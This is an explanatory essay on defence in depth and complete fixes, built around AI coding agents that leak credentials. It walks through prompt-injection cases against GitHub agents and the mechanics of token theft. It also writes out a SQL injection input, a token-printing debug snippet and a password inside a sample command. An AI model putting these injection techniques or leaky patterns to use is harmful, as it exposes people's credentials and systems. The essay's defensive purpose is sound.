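# Defence in depth and complete fixes in security design: the case of AI agents that leak credentials

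## Agents, credentials and what counts as a complete fix

In computer security, defence in depth means using several protections so that the failure of one does not cause the loss. A bank does this when it has both a guard at the door and a lock on the vault. The alternative is to remove the cause of the problem so that the attack no longer works. This is usually better where it is possible. Often, though, the cause cannot be removed, or can be removed only later or only in part, and designers then have to judge how much value the layers add.

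A growing number of software projects face that decision because they use AI agents that hold passwords and access keys. An *agent* is a language model connected to tools, so that its output runs commands, reads files or calls services. To do useful work, it often needs a *credential*, which is anything that proves identity or authority to a service, such as a password, an API key (a string that one program presents to use another), an access token or a private key. Agents sometimes leak these credentials. Only part of that problem currently has a complete fix, and which part depends on what "complete" means.

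### A coding agent that reads bug reports

GitHub is a website where software projects keep their code. Anyone with an account can file a bug report there, which GitHub calls an issue, and a popular project may receive more issues than its maintainers can read. Many projects therefore run an agent that reads each new issue, labels it, searches for duplicates and in some cases writes the fix. The running example from here on is a coding agent of this kind, which can use a GitHub token and regularly reads text from strangers.

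The *harness* is the ordinary software around the model. It runs the model's tool calls and holds the permissions, approval rules and logs. When an issue arrives, the harness combines its text with the developer's instructions and other material. GitHub says its Copilot cloud agent combines the task from an issue or comment with other relevant information to form a prompt, then sends the prompt to a language model. The model returns text. If that text contains a request to use a tool, such as to run a command, the harness runs the command and adds the output to what the model reads next. The model's *context window* is everything it reads at one time, including instructions, documents and tool output.

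The GitHub token lets the agent act on the project's repository, which stores its code and history. It is a *bearer token*, a credential that works for whoever holds it. A stranger who obtains it can do whatever it allows the agent to do, until it expires or somebody revokes it. Nakibly and Babo (2026) report in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* that agents on GitHub commonly hold such a token, and that any account can start many of them by opening an issue.

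This exposes the agent to *prompt injection*, in which an agent follows instructions planted in content it reads as if they came from its user. The attack is possible because a model receives instructions and data in a single stream of text and cannot reliably tell them apart. In July 2026 somebody filed a bug report with Gemini CLI, a Google coding agent whose code is public. A maintainer looking at the page saw an ordinary complaint about API keys that contain special characters. The raw text, which the project's agents receive, also contained a comment that GitHub does not display. The comment was addressed to the agent that looks for duplicate issues and was an attempt to obtain that agent's token.

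Such attacks are rare. Nakibly and Babo searched 142.7 million issues, comments and pull requests (proposed changes to a project's code), read the 5,251 most suspicious items by hand, and confirmed 43 attacks on other people's agents, or about one in 3.3 million items. Nineteen of the 43 tried to get the agent's secrets. When they replayed all 43 attacks offline, using five models in place of the targeted agents, only one small, fast model followed any of the attackers' instructions, and it did so in 19% of the attacks.

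Those numbers are a fair argument against panic, but the census counted only text hidden from human readers, so it would miss an injection written in plain view. An average over all of GitHub is also a poor guide to a prominent project's own risk. Nineteen of the attacks targeted repositories of six large technology companies. Nine used the real names of the victim agent's tools or output fields, so their writers had studied the project's configuration. One successful attack can also be enough to take over a repository. The Hacker News (2026) reported in February that Orca Security, a security company, did this by hiding instructions in an issue that made GitHub's Copilot assistant leak its token.

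### What makes a fix complete

An attacker can exploit the agent's token by *theft*, obtaining the credential itself, or by *misuse*, getting the agent to use its access on the attacker's behalf. With misuse, the attacker may never see the token. For example, the agent deletes a branch or approves a change because an issue contains instructions to do so, and GitHub carries out the request because the agent has the authority. An older security term for such an agent is a *confused deputy*, a privileged program that someone without the necessary authority induces to act for them.

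A *complete fix* is a change after which a stated attacker cannot break a stated security property, so long as the fix works as designed. A *partial mitigation* makes an attack less likely, harder or less harmful, but leaves it possible by design. The attacker and the property must be stated because no change can make a laptop secure in every respect. Microsoft can, however, set a precise goal for BitLocker, the disk encryption in Windows, which is that nobody can obtain the encrypted data while the device is turned off. That goal covers a thief who steals a laptop that is turned off. If he steals one that is unlocked and running and reads the files, BitLocker has not failed, because its goal does not cover that case.

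One measure can therefore be a complete fix for one property and a partial mitigation for another. GitHub says that Copilot cloud agent never receives text entered as an HTML comment, the kind of hidden text in the Gemini CLI report. If this filter works, it is a complete fix for the property "no instruction hidden in an HTML comment reaches the agent". It is only a partial mitigation for the property "no stranger's instruction steers the agent", because a stranger can write the instruction in visible text and hope that nobody reads the issue closely. When Nakibly and Babo stripped HTML comments from their 43 attacks, compliance fell to zero. That is a good result for the narrower property but hardly evidence about the broader one, since attackers who expected the filter would not have hidden their instructions.

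A *credential broker* also solves only part of the problem. It is a separate component that holds the real credential and adds it to the agent's requests after they leave the agent's environment. An attacker who takes over the agent finds no credential there to steal, but can still have the agent send a harmful request, and the broker will attach the credential to that request. Preventing theft can therefore make the whole system seem safer than it is. Saltzer and Schroeder warned of this danger in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), writing that concentrating on protection mechanisms, especially ones that are logically impossible to defeat, "may lead to false confidence in the system as a whole".

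Some practitioners use a looser standard. Salesforce's *Mitigate the Threats*, a training page for developers, counts a mitigation as total if it puts a threat out of attackers' reach, for example by making it too expensive. But an attack that is too expensive for one attacker may not be for another, and attacks tend to get cheaper. In one of the page's examples, an attacker intercepts the link that lets a blog author reset a password. The page prescribes an encrypted connection and a one-hour limit on the link, labels each of them partial, and then concludes that together they mitigate the threat. These measures reduce the threat, but the link is also a bearer credential, so if the author forwards it to the wrong person, it will work for the rest of the hour.

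Such a case still leaves a *residual risk*, the risk that remains once the protections are in place. Salesforce's advice to either redesign the system or accept the risk in writing, with the agreement of executives, is sound.

### SQL injection with and without its cause

The standard example of a complete fix in software comes from databases. Programs query databases in a language called SQL, and a careless program builds its query by joining pieces of text:

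```
query = "SELECT account_balance FROM user_data
         WHERE user_name = '" + name + "'"
```

If a customer types `alice`, the database looks up Alice's balance. If the customer types `tom' or '1'='1`, the joined text ends like this:

```
WHERE user_name = 'tom' or '1'='1'
```

In this attack, called SQL injection, the quotation mark after `tom` closes the name early, and the rest of the input becomes part of the command. Since '1' always equals '1', the condition holds for every row, and the query returns every customer's balance. The database is working correctly, but nothing in the single piece of text it received marks where the programmer's words stop and the customer's begin.

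A developer who discovers the attack may add a filter:

```
if "' or '" in name: reject(name)
```

The filter stops that exact input but not the same input with `OR` in capitals, which means the same thing in SQL. The developer can add capitals, extra spaces and other always-true conditions to the list, but the attacker needs only one form that is missing from it. Banning quotation marks altogether turns away a customer named O'Brien, and it doesn't protect a query that looks up an account by number, because an attacker can add a condition there without quotation marks. Each repair deals with one input, but the program still builds the query by joining text, which is why such inputs work.

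A *parameterised query* does away with the joining:

```
query = "SELECT account_balance FROM user_data
         WHERE user_name = ?"
execute(query, name)
```

The program now sends the command with a placeholder in it and sends the name separately. The structure of the command is fixed before the name arrives, so the database can only compare the name with the entries in the table. Given the hostile input above, it searches for a customer whose name is literally `tom' or '1'='1` and finds nobody. According to OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a widely used guide for developers, a database queried this way always distinguishes code from data, whatever the user types. Developers don't have to maintain a list of bad inputs. OWASP strongly discourages escaping, in which the program marks special characters so that the database reads them as plain text, because this method is not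 guaranteed to prevent every injection.

OWASP points out that parameterised queries have limits. A placeholder can stand for a value but not for a table name, a column name or the sort order. In those cases the program should translate the user's choice into one of a few names written in its own code. Parameterised queries also stop user input from changing the meaning of a command, but they don't ensure that customers see only their own balances. If the program lets Tom ask for Alice's balance, he can type `alice`, and a correctly parameterised query will return it. OWASP therefore recommends limiting what the program's database account may do, as a further layer.

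US agencies have taken up the distinction between filtering input and removing the cause. CISA's *Secure by Design Alert* (2024), which the US cybersecurity agency issued with the FBI, urges software makers to use parameterised queries to prevent SQL injection. The agencies described cleaning up user input as brittle, hard to enforce at scale and often possible to bypass, as Industrial Cyber's *CISA, FBI release secure by design alert* reports. They issued the alert after a series of attacks through a file-transfer product affected thousands of organisations. CISA (2024) observed that manufacturers were still shipping the defect two decades after it became widely known.

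One reason developers keep choosing weaker measures, such as validating input, may be that they are often cheaper at first. In *A method to assess 'forgivable' vs 'unforgivable' vulnerabilities*, Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) rated common remedies by cost, familiarity and technical feasibility, from 3 for the easiest to 9 for the hardest. Validating input scored 3. Adopting a well-tested library or framework, the category that parameterised queries seem to fit best, scored 6, and choosing a safer programming language scored 8. These scores apply to new software, and the NCSC expects costs to rise steeply when a remedy is added later.

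SQL injection in a large program is also a *structural problem*, a weakness in how a system is arranged that fixing individual instances doesn't remove. A team that corrects forty queries can reintroduce the flaw in the next one by joining text, so it has to change how it writes queries in general. Prompt injection has the same structure, since a stranger's words are joined to a trusted command, but language models have no equivalent of SQL's placeholders.

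### What Microsoft undertakes to repair

A software maker that ships both kinds of protection has to tell its customers which is which, and Microsoft does so in its *Security Servicing Criteria for Windows*. Warfield, of the company's security response centre, announced the first version in September 2018, and Microsoft last revised the document in October 2024. Microsoft intends to release an update or guidance for a reported vulnerability if it violates the goal or intent of a security boundary or security feature and is severe enough. Otherwise, the company's default is to release nothing now and consider the vulnerability for a later version of Windows.

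A *security boundary* separates differently trusted parts of a system, and the system's maker promises to uphold and repair it. One such boundary prevents a program without administrator rights from reading or altering the kernel, the core of the operating system. Another prevents one running program from tampering with another without authorisation. A way across either boundary is a defect that Microsoft intends to fix, though it offers updates "where commercially reasonable" and reserves the right to decide otherwise.

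The kernel boundary also shows why a description of a boundary needs to specify the attacker. The boundary applies to programs without administrator rights, but not to programs that already have them. Administrators can switch off security features and uninstall updates, so Microsoft treats them as part of what the system has to trust.

Microsoft classes another group of protections as defence in depth, and by default does not plan to fix bypasses of them. Data Execution Prevention (DEP) stops the processor from running code from memory meant only for data, where attackers often place their own instructions. Address Space Layout Randomization (ASLR) puts a program's code and data at unpredictable addresses, so that an attacker does not know where to find the pieces an attack needs. User Account Control (UAC) asks for an administrator's consent before a program makes system-wide changes. Microsoft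 explains that such features may have limitations by design that keep them from fully stopping a threat. DEP, for instance, does not prevent an attacker from misusing code already in the program and allowed to run.

Microsoft argues that it need not repair every bypass of a feature such as DEP, because a bypass is useless to an attacker on its own. The attacker also needs a flaw that affects a real boundary, which Microsoft will repair, or some other way in, such as tricking the user. Microsoft keeps improving many of these features from release to release and pays researchers for reports about some of them, but it does not promise that the features will withstand attack.

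Comparing UAC with its successor, Administrator protection, shows how that promise helps users. Microsoft describes Administrator protection as a new security boundary. Project Zero (2026), Google's team of vulnerability researchers, found nine ways around it, and Microsoft has fixed all nine. For UAC, Project Zero points to a public collection of 81 bypass techniques, some of which still worked on the latest version of Windows 11, and adds that Microsoft never officially acknowledges fixing one. Nine bypasses are a poor start for a new boundary, but each counted as a defect, and the definition of a complete fix allows for defects through the condition "so long as the fix works as designed". However, Project Zero notes that, as of 1 December 2025, Microsoft had disabled Administrator protection while dealing with an application compatibility problem.

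### Layers and duplicates

"Defence in depth" is a military term for holding several lines, so that an enemy who breaks through one meets the next. Saltzer and Schroeder explained the reasoning for it in computing in their 1975 paper. They argued that nobody knows how to build a system without flaws, so designers should follow principles that make flaws fewer and less serious. According to *Security Design Principles* (2012), Saltzer had drawn up five such principles in 1974 from his work on Multics, an early time-sharing system. The 1975 paper has eight, and two of them matter most for the coding agent.

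*Least privilege* means that every program and user should have only the privileges its job requires. An agent that labels issues needs permission to do that, but not to change code. The limit helps against both theft and misuse, because neither a thief nor a hijacked agent can do more with a token than it allows. GitHub applies the principle to Copilot cloud agent, which can push changes to only one branch and cannot approve or merge its own work.

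*Complete mediation* means that the system checks that every access to every object is authorized. For the agent, this check has to happen outside the model. A prompt instruction not to touch the main branch isn't mediation because it works only if the model follows it, whereas a check on GitHub's servers applies whatever the model writes. Saltzer and Schroeder added that the system needs a foolproof way to identify the source of every request. Bearer tokens meet this condition poorly, because a valid token shows only that the sender has it, not whether the sender is the agent or a thief. When a stranger's prompt leads the agent to misuse its token, the request does come from the agent, but nothing in it identifies the stranger.

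Adding more protections does not always add layers. Under Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of *separation of privilege*, a mechanism that needs two keys is stronger than one that needs a single key, because different people or programs can hold the keys, and then no single accident, deception or breach of trust is enough to compromise it. This benefit depends on keeping the keys apart, since a second lock that opens with the same key as the first only delays a burglar who has that key by a few seconds.

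Suppose the maintainers of the coding agent install two filters that both look for phrases from earlier injections. A new wording that gets past one will probably get past the other, so the second filter adds little protection against new wordings. Engineers call it a *common-cause failure* when one event or technique defeats several layers at once. A firewall that restricts where the agent can send data is unaffected by the injection's wording, so an attacker who wants the token must also find a way to send it out through a permitted destination.

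Whether two measures are separate layers depends on the attack. The filter and the firewall are different kinds of obstacle to theft, but the firewall does nothing against misuse inside GitHub itself, because the agent has to reach GitHub to work. A designer can check for this by writing down, for each measure and each attack, what would have to go wrong for the measure to fail. If the same event would defeat both measures, they count as one for that event.

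Layers also differ in how visibly they fail. Saltzer and Schroeder advised designers to refuse access by default and list what is allowed. A mistake in such a list tends to shut out somebody who should get in, and that person complains. A mistake in a list of forbidden things lets somebody in, and nobody may notice. GitHub uses both kinds of rule for Copilot cloud agent. Only people with write access to the repository can give the agent work, and GitHub never passes it comments from anyone else. If that rule wrongly excludes a maintainer, GitHub will hear about it the same day. GitHub also filters out hidden text. If the filter misses a new way of hiding text, the agent reads it, and the first sign of the failure may be a leaked token in use elsewhere.

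## How credentials leak from agents

By the time somebody misuses an agent's credential, several copies of it may exist in places that nobody set up to hold secrets. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) divides a leak into five stages. In *introduction*, a reusable secret enters text or files that the agent can read. In *propagation*, the systems around the agent copy it. The *trigger* is whatever makes the agent disclose or misuse it. In *execution*, a service accepts the credential and carries out a request. In *persistence*, the credential keeps working afterwards, away from the agent and outside the owner's control.

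These authors work for Corvic AI, which sells a product that keeps credentials away from agents, so they have a commercial interest in the problem. But anyone can check the chain by following one credential through it, such as the GitHub token of the coding agent that reads bug reports.

### How the token reaches the agent

The maintainers have to give the agent some way to use its token. They can paste it into a chat message or the agent's standing instructions, write it into a configuration file, or set it as an environment variable, which is a named value that a program passes to the programs it starts. These methods are all quick and put the token where the agent can read it.

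An agent can also come across secrets that nobody meant to give it, because developers often leave them in code. Kenney and colleagues cite GitGuardian, a company that looks for exposed secrets, which found 23,770,171 of them in public GitHub commits (saved sets of changes) made during 2024, 25% more than the year before. GitGuardian also found at least one secret in 4.61% of the 69.6 million public repositories it scanned, or about 3.2 million.

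GitGuardian's count is a vendor's measurement, and it depends on what the company's detectors recognise, what it classes as a secret and how it treats duplicates. Finding a string that looks like a key doesn't show that the key still worked or that anybody abused it. The count also covers public software in general, so it doesn't directly measure how often agents leak. Given the count, though, an agent that reads many repositories will probably read somebody's password sooner or later.

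Secrets can also leak from where a platform stores them. In June 2024 Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, disclosed unauthorised access to the secrets of Spaces, its service for hosting small applications, and advised affected users to replace them. Kenney and colleagues note that the incident doesn't establish that the intruder took or used every secret, and that no model revealed anything. The incident is still relevant to agents because a platform that hosts many of them holds many of their credentials in one place.

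### The copies that follow

Suppose the token is in a configuration file, and the agent opens the file to check which version of a library the project uses. The agent needs one line. The harness gives the model the whole file, token included, because that is what the command returned. Nobody has attacked anything, and the agent has done what its user asked, but the token is now in the context window. From there it can spread to the other kinds of copy that Kenney and colleagues list. Who can read each copy depends on how the maintainers have set up the agent, but these are typical cases:

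| Copy | How the token gets there | Who may be able to read it |
|---|---|---|
| Context window | The harness adds the file's contents to the model's next input | The company that runs the model, any company that forwards the request, and anyone who can get the agent to repeat the text |
| Conversation history and logs | The harness saves each tool call with its output | The maintainers, the people who run the logging system, and anyone who breaks into it |
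| Memory | The agent saves notes or passages for later sessions | Later users, if they share the agent's memory |
| Generated code | The model writes the token into a script as a fixed value | Everyone who can read the repository |
| Error messages | A failed request comes back with its address or headers, which contain the token | Whoever receives the error report |

Most of these systems are designed to store and retrieve text, which makes them a bad place for a password. If the maintainers notice the token in the configuration file and delete it, the copies in these systems remain.

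### Why debugging output leaks secrets

The largest body of evidence on how ordinary code makes these copies comes from agent skills. A skill is a package that a user installs to give an agent a new ability. It contains written instructions for the model and usually scripts for the agent to run. Many harnesses run these scripts directly on the user's computer, where the scripts can read the same environment variables and configuration files as the program that started them.

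*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) examines a random sample of 17,022 skills from the 170,226 on SkillsMP, a large public marketplace, in February 2026. The researchers first searched the skills' instructions and code for signs of credentials and ruled out 8,343 skills that had none. They then checked the rest for code that passed a credential to a function that prints, saves or sends data, and for written instructions that mentioned a credential close to a verb such as "send" or "log", or contained phrases typical of prompt injection and social engineering. That left 3,156 candidates.

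The researchers then ran each candidate in a sandbox, an isolated environment, using the coding agent Claude Code. They supplied fake credentials with a marker unique to each skill, so they could trace any leak to its source. Each skill ran three times on a normal task and three times with a hostile instruction planted in material it read, such as a web page. Suspicious behaviour appeared in 1,427 candidates. Three of the researchers reviewed all of these by hand and cleared 907, typically because the skill had sent a credential where its documentation said it would and where its job required. The remaining 520 skills, 3.1% of the sample, leaked credentials. Of these, 437 did so through carelessness and 83 were malicious.

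The careless skills had 1,371 separate issues between them, and 1,007 of those, or 73.5%, were credentials exposed in output, mainly through debugging messages. (The share is 59% if the issues in malicious skills count as well.) The typical mistake looks harmless:

```
headers = {"Authorization": "Bearer " + token}
print(headers)        # left in after debugging
response = get(url, headers)
```

A developer whose program cannot log in to a service will often print the login data to see what is wrong. When she runs the program herself on her own computer, only she sees the output. When an agent runs the same script, the harness adds everything the script prints to the context window, because the model needs the output to tell whether the command worked. But the harness doesn't distinguish a test result from a token, so one forgotten print statement puts the token into the context window every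 time the skill runs.

One skill in the sample, which connects an agent to Google's office software, printed both an access token and a refresh token, the longer-lasting credential that a program uses to obtain new access tokens. An attacker who can talk to the agent can then simply ask what the output contained. Chen and colleagues confirmed in the sandbox that a planted instruction could also extract the tokens.

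Three kinds of mistake made up the rest. In 107 skills, the developers had written a credential directly into the code or documentation. Another 77 passed credentials in places such as command-line arguments, which other programs on the same computer may be able to read. Five left credentials in files, and one of these wrote a private key for signing software to a temporary directory that any user of the machine can read on most Unix systems.

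Chen and colleagues also report that 72% of the cases with credentials in the code showed signs of AI assistance in the project's history, and they suggest that coding assistants spread the habit of putting credentials there. They may be right, but the figure is weak evidence because people who write skills for AI agents probably use AI assistants a great deal anyway. It means little unless we know what share of the clean skills showed the same signs.

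The overall rate of 3.1% should be read with similar care, because it comes from one marketplace and gives a skill that nobody installs the same weight as a popular one. It probably also misses some leaks, since the code analysis covered only Python and JavaScript and did not follow credentials once the program had copied them into another variable. The explanation for the debugging leaks is more reliable than the rate, because it applies to any harness that returns printed output to the model.

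### What came back from two million prompts

Once the token is in the context window, it also leaves the maintainers' computers, unless they run the model themselves. The harness sends the text to an inference provider, a company that charges for running models on its own hardware. Sometimes the request goes through a router or reseller, which forwards it to whichever provider is cheapest or available. The maintainers cannot see what any of these companies does with the text.

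From July to November 2026, a team led by HD Moore, chief research officer at the security company Dragos, sent nearly two million prompts to AI services and put bait in them, including web addresses, passwords and keys for AWS, Amazon's cloud service. Security researchers call such bait a *canary token*. Nobody has a legitimate reason to use it, so any use shows that a person or program has read the text containing it. Moore sent each secret in only one request to one provider, according to UA.News' *Study finds secret leaks in AI service chains*, which relays a report by Ars Technica. He could therefore trace a stolen key to a single request.

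*Three breaches, endless leaks* (Moore, 2026) summarises the findings as three breaches at providers, theft of prompts, and "Zero Data Retention" settings that providers ignored. These settings are supposed to stop a provider from storing a customer's prompts or the model's answers.

The breaches are the most serious of these findings. Cybernews' *AI routers are leaking your passwords. Here's the proof* reports that in the largest breach, attackers stole a couple of hundred AWS keys and tested some of them within hours. Some of the stolen secrets came from requests that the provider had rejected before a model ran. Moore concludes that the attackers were copying data at the point where requests enter the provider's systems. If he is right, even a model immune to prompt injection would not have prevented those leaks.

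The break-ins began as early as mid-July. According to Cornelißen's German news article *Dragos* (2026), none of the three providers knew about them until Dragos got in touch. Their customers could hardly have known either. Dragos believes the attackers almost certainly copied real customers' prompts too, since the providers processed those prompts alongside the bait.

Some leaks required no break-in. Several resellers on a marketplace for AI services could read and keep their customers' prompts using the marketplace's standard logging. To find out which resellers were involved, Moore's team sent identical requests to the same model through different resellers and checked which routes led to someone using the bait. So the logs in the table above can belong to a company the maintainers have never heard of.

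The evidence about privacy settings is harder to interpret. Between July and October, a Chinese AI laboratory's systems visited the bait addresses from more than half of the requests sent to its models, and from about two thirds of those marked as private. A visit is weaker evidence than the use of a stolen key, because an automated program may have followed the link without anyone reading the prompt. But some visits came long after the request. One link drew a visit from China 24 days later, as Techno-Science's *Secrets entrusted to AI exploited by strangers* reports, and another turned up in a company's internal chat, so somebody had kept those prompts. Some of the requests had gone to US providers that resold the Chinese laboratory's models, which is why Moore says that "a privacy flag only binds the first hop".

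OpenRouter, which routes requests to many providers, responded on 22 November by removing three of them. It also withdrew 125 endpoints (connections to particular models at particular providers) from its Zero Data Retention list, some only as a precaution. It says its own systems were not involved. Network Security Magazine's *OpenRouter Drops 3 Providers After Researchers Catch Months of Prompt Theft* notes that neither OpenRouter nor Dragos has named the three providers.

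This evidence does not show that every provider leaks credentials, and the number of prompts cannot be used to estimate how many do. Dragos also sells security products, so it has a commercial interest in the result. But its method makes an innocent explanation of the stolen keys unlikely, so the experiment matters for the coding agent. If a harness sends a live token to a compromised provider, a thief can use it within hours.

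### What sets off a leak

A token in a log or a context window does no harm until somebody obtains it or the agent passes it on. Kenney and colleagues name four possible triggers for a leak: prompt injection, a request that gets the agent to reveal its standing instructions, a malicious response from a tool, and an ordinary mistake by the model.

For the coding agent, a deliberate trigger could be a bug report that asks for the contents of the configuration file "to help reproduce the problem". If the agent posts them as a comment on a public project, anyone can copy the token. An accidental trigger could be a failed command, after which the agent posts a comment with the full error message, including the header that contains the token. An agent that fills in web forms runs a similar risk. It has to read the values it types, so it can put a password into the wrong field or submit it to the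 wrong site.

In the skills study, nearly half of the careless skills (200 of 437) leaked a credential without an attacker, in at least two of their three normal runs. The other 237 leaked at most once in the normal runs, but did so in at least one run with a planted instruction.

Chen and colleagues also report that 466 of the 520 affected skills leak during normal execution. This is hard to reconcile with their own tests, in which only 283 skills, careless and malicious together, met their threshold for leaking under normal conditions, so the lower figure is safer to use.

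One of the 83 malicious skills claimed to fetch weather forecasts, but its code read the user's credential file and sent the contents to an attacker. An attacker who uses a skill like this doesn't have to persuade the model to reveal anything, because the user has installed the attacker's code and the agent runs it. Reading only the skill's description would not reveal the theft. In 76.3% of the affected skills, the researchers had to examine the instructions and the code together to find the leak.

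The attackers who stole Moore's keys used no trigger, because they took the keys straight from copies at the providers without making any agent do anything. The five stages are therefore a common route, but not every leak follows them.

### What a thief does with a credential

In the execution stage, a thief can do whatever the credential allows, such as reading private code or publishing a new version of the software. The bait keys showed Moore's team what attackers try first. The attackers sent AWS tens of thousands of requests with the keys. They looked for stored files. They also searched two AWS services where companies keep further passwords and settings, hoping to turn one stolen credential into several. Finally, they tried to switch on AI models in the account, which they would then have been able to use at the owner's expense.

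The attackers also added their own user accounts so that their access could outlast the original key. An owner who discovers the theft and cancels the key also has to find whatever the attackers created while the key worked.

Even without such extra steps, a thief may have plenty of time to use a leaked credential, because many owners are slow to cancel it. Kenney and colleagues cite earlier academic research which found that many secrets in public GitHub repositories were still valid long after developers published them.

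Deleting a published secret doesn't solve this, partly because other developers may already have copied it. On GitHub, anyone can *fork* a public repository, which creates a separate copy under their own account. If the original developer later removes a token, the fork still contains it unless the fork's owner brings in the newer version. Chen and colleagues report that developers removed credentials from 107 repositories after the researchers alerted the marketplace, but that the same credentials remained in more than 50 independent forks.

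The paper's figures are slightly inconsistent, since it also gives a repair rate of 91.6% for credentials in code, which would be 98 of the 107 skills. A credential in a fork does no harm if its owner has cancelled it. Whichever figure is right, removing the text repairs only one copy, while cancelling the credential makes every copy useless, including those nobody has found.

Malicious code survives in the same way. One skill posed as a cryptocurrency trading tool, and after a report about it, the maintainers of the site that listed it banned its publisher. The researchers found its hidden payload in 330 files across 70 repositories, under 15 skill names, so a search for the original name would have missed most of them.

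### Two structural causes

These leaks happen because developers leave reusable secrets where the agent can read them and let the agent act on text from strangers. Both problems are in the agent's design, so even after a developer deletes one debugging line or blocks one hostile phrase, the next skill or bug report can still cause a leak.

Accidental leaks require only that the secret be readable. If the maintainers moved the coding agent to a private project where only trusted colleagues can file reports, no stranger's text would reach it. But the forgotten debugging line would still print the token, the harness would add it to the context window, and the next request would carry it to the provider. An intruder copying requests there would then have the token. Better resistance to prompt injection would not help either, because this leak involves no injection.

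Theft by prompt injection usually needs both features, since the stranger has to reach the agent and the agent has to be able to read the token. Designers can try to stop it at either point, but keeping the token out of the agent's reach looks much more promising at present. That is ordinary engineering, whereas researchers disagree about whether models can ever learn to reliably tell a user's instructions from a stranger's. Kenney and colleagues argue that keeping the token out of reach eliminates the introduction and propagation stages by design, and they tested this on a small scale with their own company's product. If the token never enters the agent's environment, the debugging line cannot print it and the hostile bug report cannot extract it. Misuse remains possible because it does not require a readable secret.

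## Scanning for secrets and redacting them

Maintainers can only withhold credentials they know about, but an agent may also read a forgotten password in a file. To find such passwords, teams use a *secret scanner*, a program that searches text for strings that look like credentials. When it finds one, it can block the text, alert somebody, or *redact* the string by replacing it with a placeholder.

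### How a scanner recognises a secret

Secrets are easiest to recognise when their issuers give them a fixed format. Many GitHub tokens begin with `ghp_`, and many AWS key identifiers begin with `AKIA`. A scanner checks the text against a rule for each format, such as "`ghp_` followed by 36 letters and digits". These rules raise few false alarms because hardly any other text matches them.

Passwords and many keys have no fixed format, so scanners also test how random a string looks. The usual measure is *entropy*, in bits per character:

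```
H = − Σ p(c) × log2 p(c)
```

Here p(c) is the share of the string's characters that are the character c, and the sum runs over every different character in the string. A string with many different characters scores high, and one that repeats a few characters scores low. These three invented strings show how the test can go wrong:

| String | What it is | Entropy |
|---|---|---|
| `q7Zt2LmX9vKd4RbN` | A randomly generated key | 4.00 |
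| `medical_database` | The name of a database | 3.25 |
| `Sup3rS3cr3t!` | A password that a person made up | 2.86 |

With a threshold of 3.5, the scanner catches the key but misses the password. Lowering the threshold to 2.8 catches the password but also flags the database name and a lot of ordinary text. Even the higher threshold causes false alarms, because the long identifier that Git computes for each commit looks random but is not secret.

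Scanners therefore also look at the surrounding words. A string that follows `password =` is more suspicious than the same string in a list of file names. But harmless instructions such as "you will need an API key" contain the same words as real leaks. Partly for this reason, only 6% of the skills that the first keyword search flagged in the skills study turned out to leak credentials. When Chen and colleagues added tests of context and excluded comments and placeholders such as `your-api-key-here`, the share rose to 16%. These percentages don't measure how well a commercial scanner works, because the researchers were looking for leaks, which is a harder task than finding stored secrets.

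Finally, some scanners check whether a key works by sending a harmless request to the service that issued it. TruffleHog, a widely used open-source scanner, has an option to report only the secrets that pass this check, as Smetanskyi notes in *Secrets & Leak Prevention*. Passing is strong evidence that a secret works, but a working secret can fail if the scanner cannot reach the service. The password to a database inside a company's network will usually fail a check from outside, so a team that uses this option may never learn that the scanner found it.

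Scanning rules check a string's prefix, its entropy and the words near it, but a string is a secret because some service accepts it. If a database accepts the password `sunshine`, then `sunshine` is a secret, though nothing in the word shows that. A secret can also appear in an altered form. For example, many programs log in to a website by encoding the username and password together as one string, which a rule written for the original password won't match. Better rules will catch more secrets but can't catch them all, so scanning can only be a partial mitigation.

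### Where to put the scanner

*Your secrets are leaking to AI coding agents*, a post by Sonar, which sells code-checking tools, recommends scanning for secrets as a developer types, before an agent sends its context to a model, before a commit, and at the pull request. An agent's logs and tool output also need checking because they hold copies of secrets too.

Scanning each prompt just before the harness sends it can keep recognisable tokens from reaching the inference provider. This would have protected customers of the breached providers that Moore discovered, at least if their keys were in common formats. The scan also covers text from every source, including files, bug reports and forgotten debugging lines.

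A filter on tool output works earlier, before the text enters the context window. Prismor's *TrapDoor*, another vendor's post, describes one for Claude Code. The model writes a placeholder, such as `@@SECRET:stripe_key@@`, in its command, and a program replaces it with the real key just before the command runs. If the command prints the key, the filter changes it back to the placeholder before the output reaches the model or the logs.

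Unlike ordinary scanners, this filter searches for exact values that it already has, so it can find a password that looks like an ordinary word. If the password is `test`, however, it will also remove every other "test" from the output. The filter can be a complete fix if the goal is only to keep a particular key from appearing as written in this command's output. It doesn't protect secrets that are missing from its list, or a listed secret that the command prints in encoded form.

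Scanning logs cleans up after a secret has been saved. Ishannaik's *Every AI coding agent writes the secrets you paste* describes a free tool that searches the saved conversations of about 30 coding agents using about 191 rules, most of them from Gitleaks, a popular open-source scanner. Ishannaik developed the tool himself and doesn't measure how well it works. It can replace a secret in the saved file but keeps a backup, so a user who wants the secret gone has to delete the backup too.

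Scans before a commit are the most established kind. Gitleaks can check the changes that a developer has selected for the next commit, and Codegen's *Trufflehog Secret Scanning* describes an agent platform with TruffleHog built in. Since March 2026, GitHub (2026) has offered a preview feature that lets a coding agent send its changes to GitHub's scanner before it commits them. This check depends on the model following a prompt or instructions to run it. A check on the server doesn't have this weakness. GitLab offers one that examines the content of every push (an upload of commits), as its *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* explains.

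Even a perfect check at this point would come too late to keep the token out of the prompt. If the agent read the token while writing the code, the harness has probably already sent it to the provider.

### Passwords in ordinary commands

A study of Claude Code's settings files tests scanners on the secrets that suit them least. Claude Code asks for permission before it runs most commands. A user who is tired of answering can choose "Yes, and don't ask again", and Claude Code then saves a rule in a file called `.claude/settings.local.json` in the project folder. Sometimes the rule is a general pattern, such as `npm test *`. In other cases it is the exact command, including any password in it. Blanco (2026), in *Claude Code guarda comandos con credenciales en el proyecto*, gives an example, which looks like this when shortened:

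```
"allow": ["Bash(PGPASSWORD=Sup3rS3cr3t! pg_dump -U app app > backup.sql)"]
```

This command makes a backup of a database. The file is meant to stay on the developer's computer, but many developers have published it along with their code. On 5 November 2026, Shmulik Cohen and Matan Giladi of the security company Apiiro reported finding 104,185 public copies on GitHub, in 103,617 repositories. Of these, 1,122 (1.1%) contained at least one secret, and together they held 1,379 different secrets. Half of the affected repositories had exposed the file for at least 217 days.

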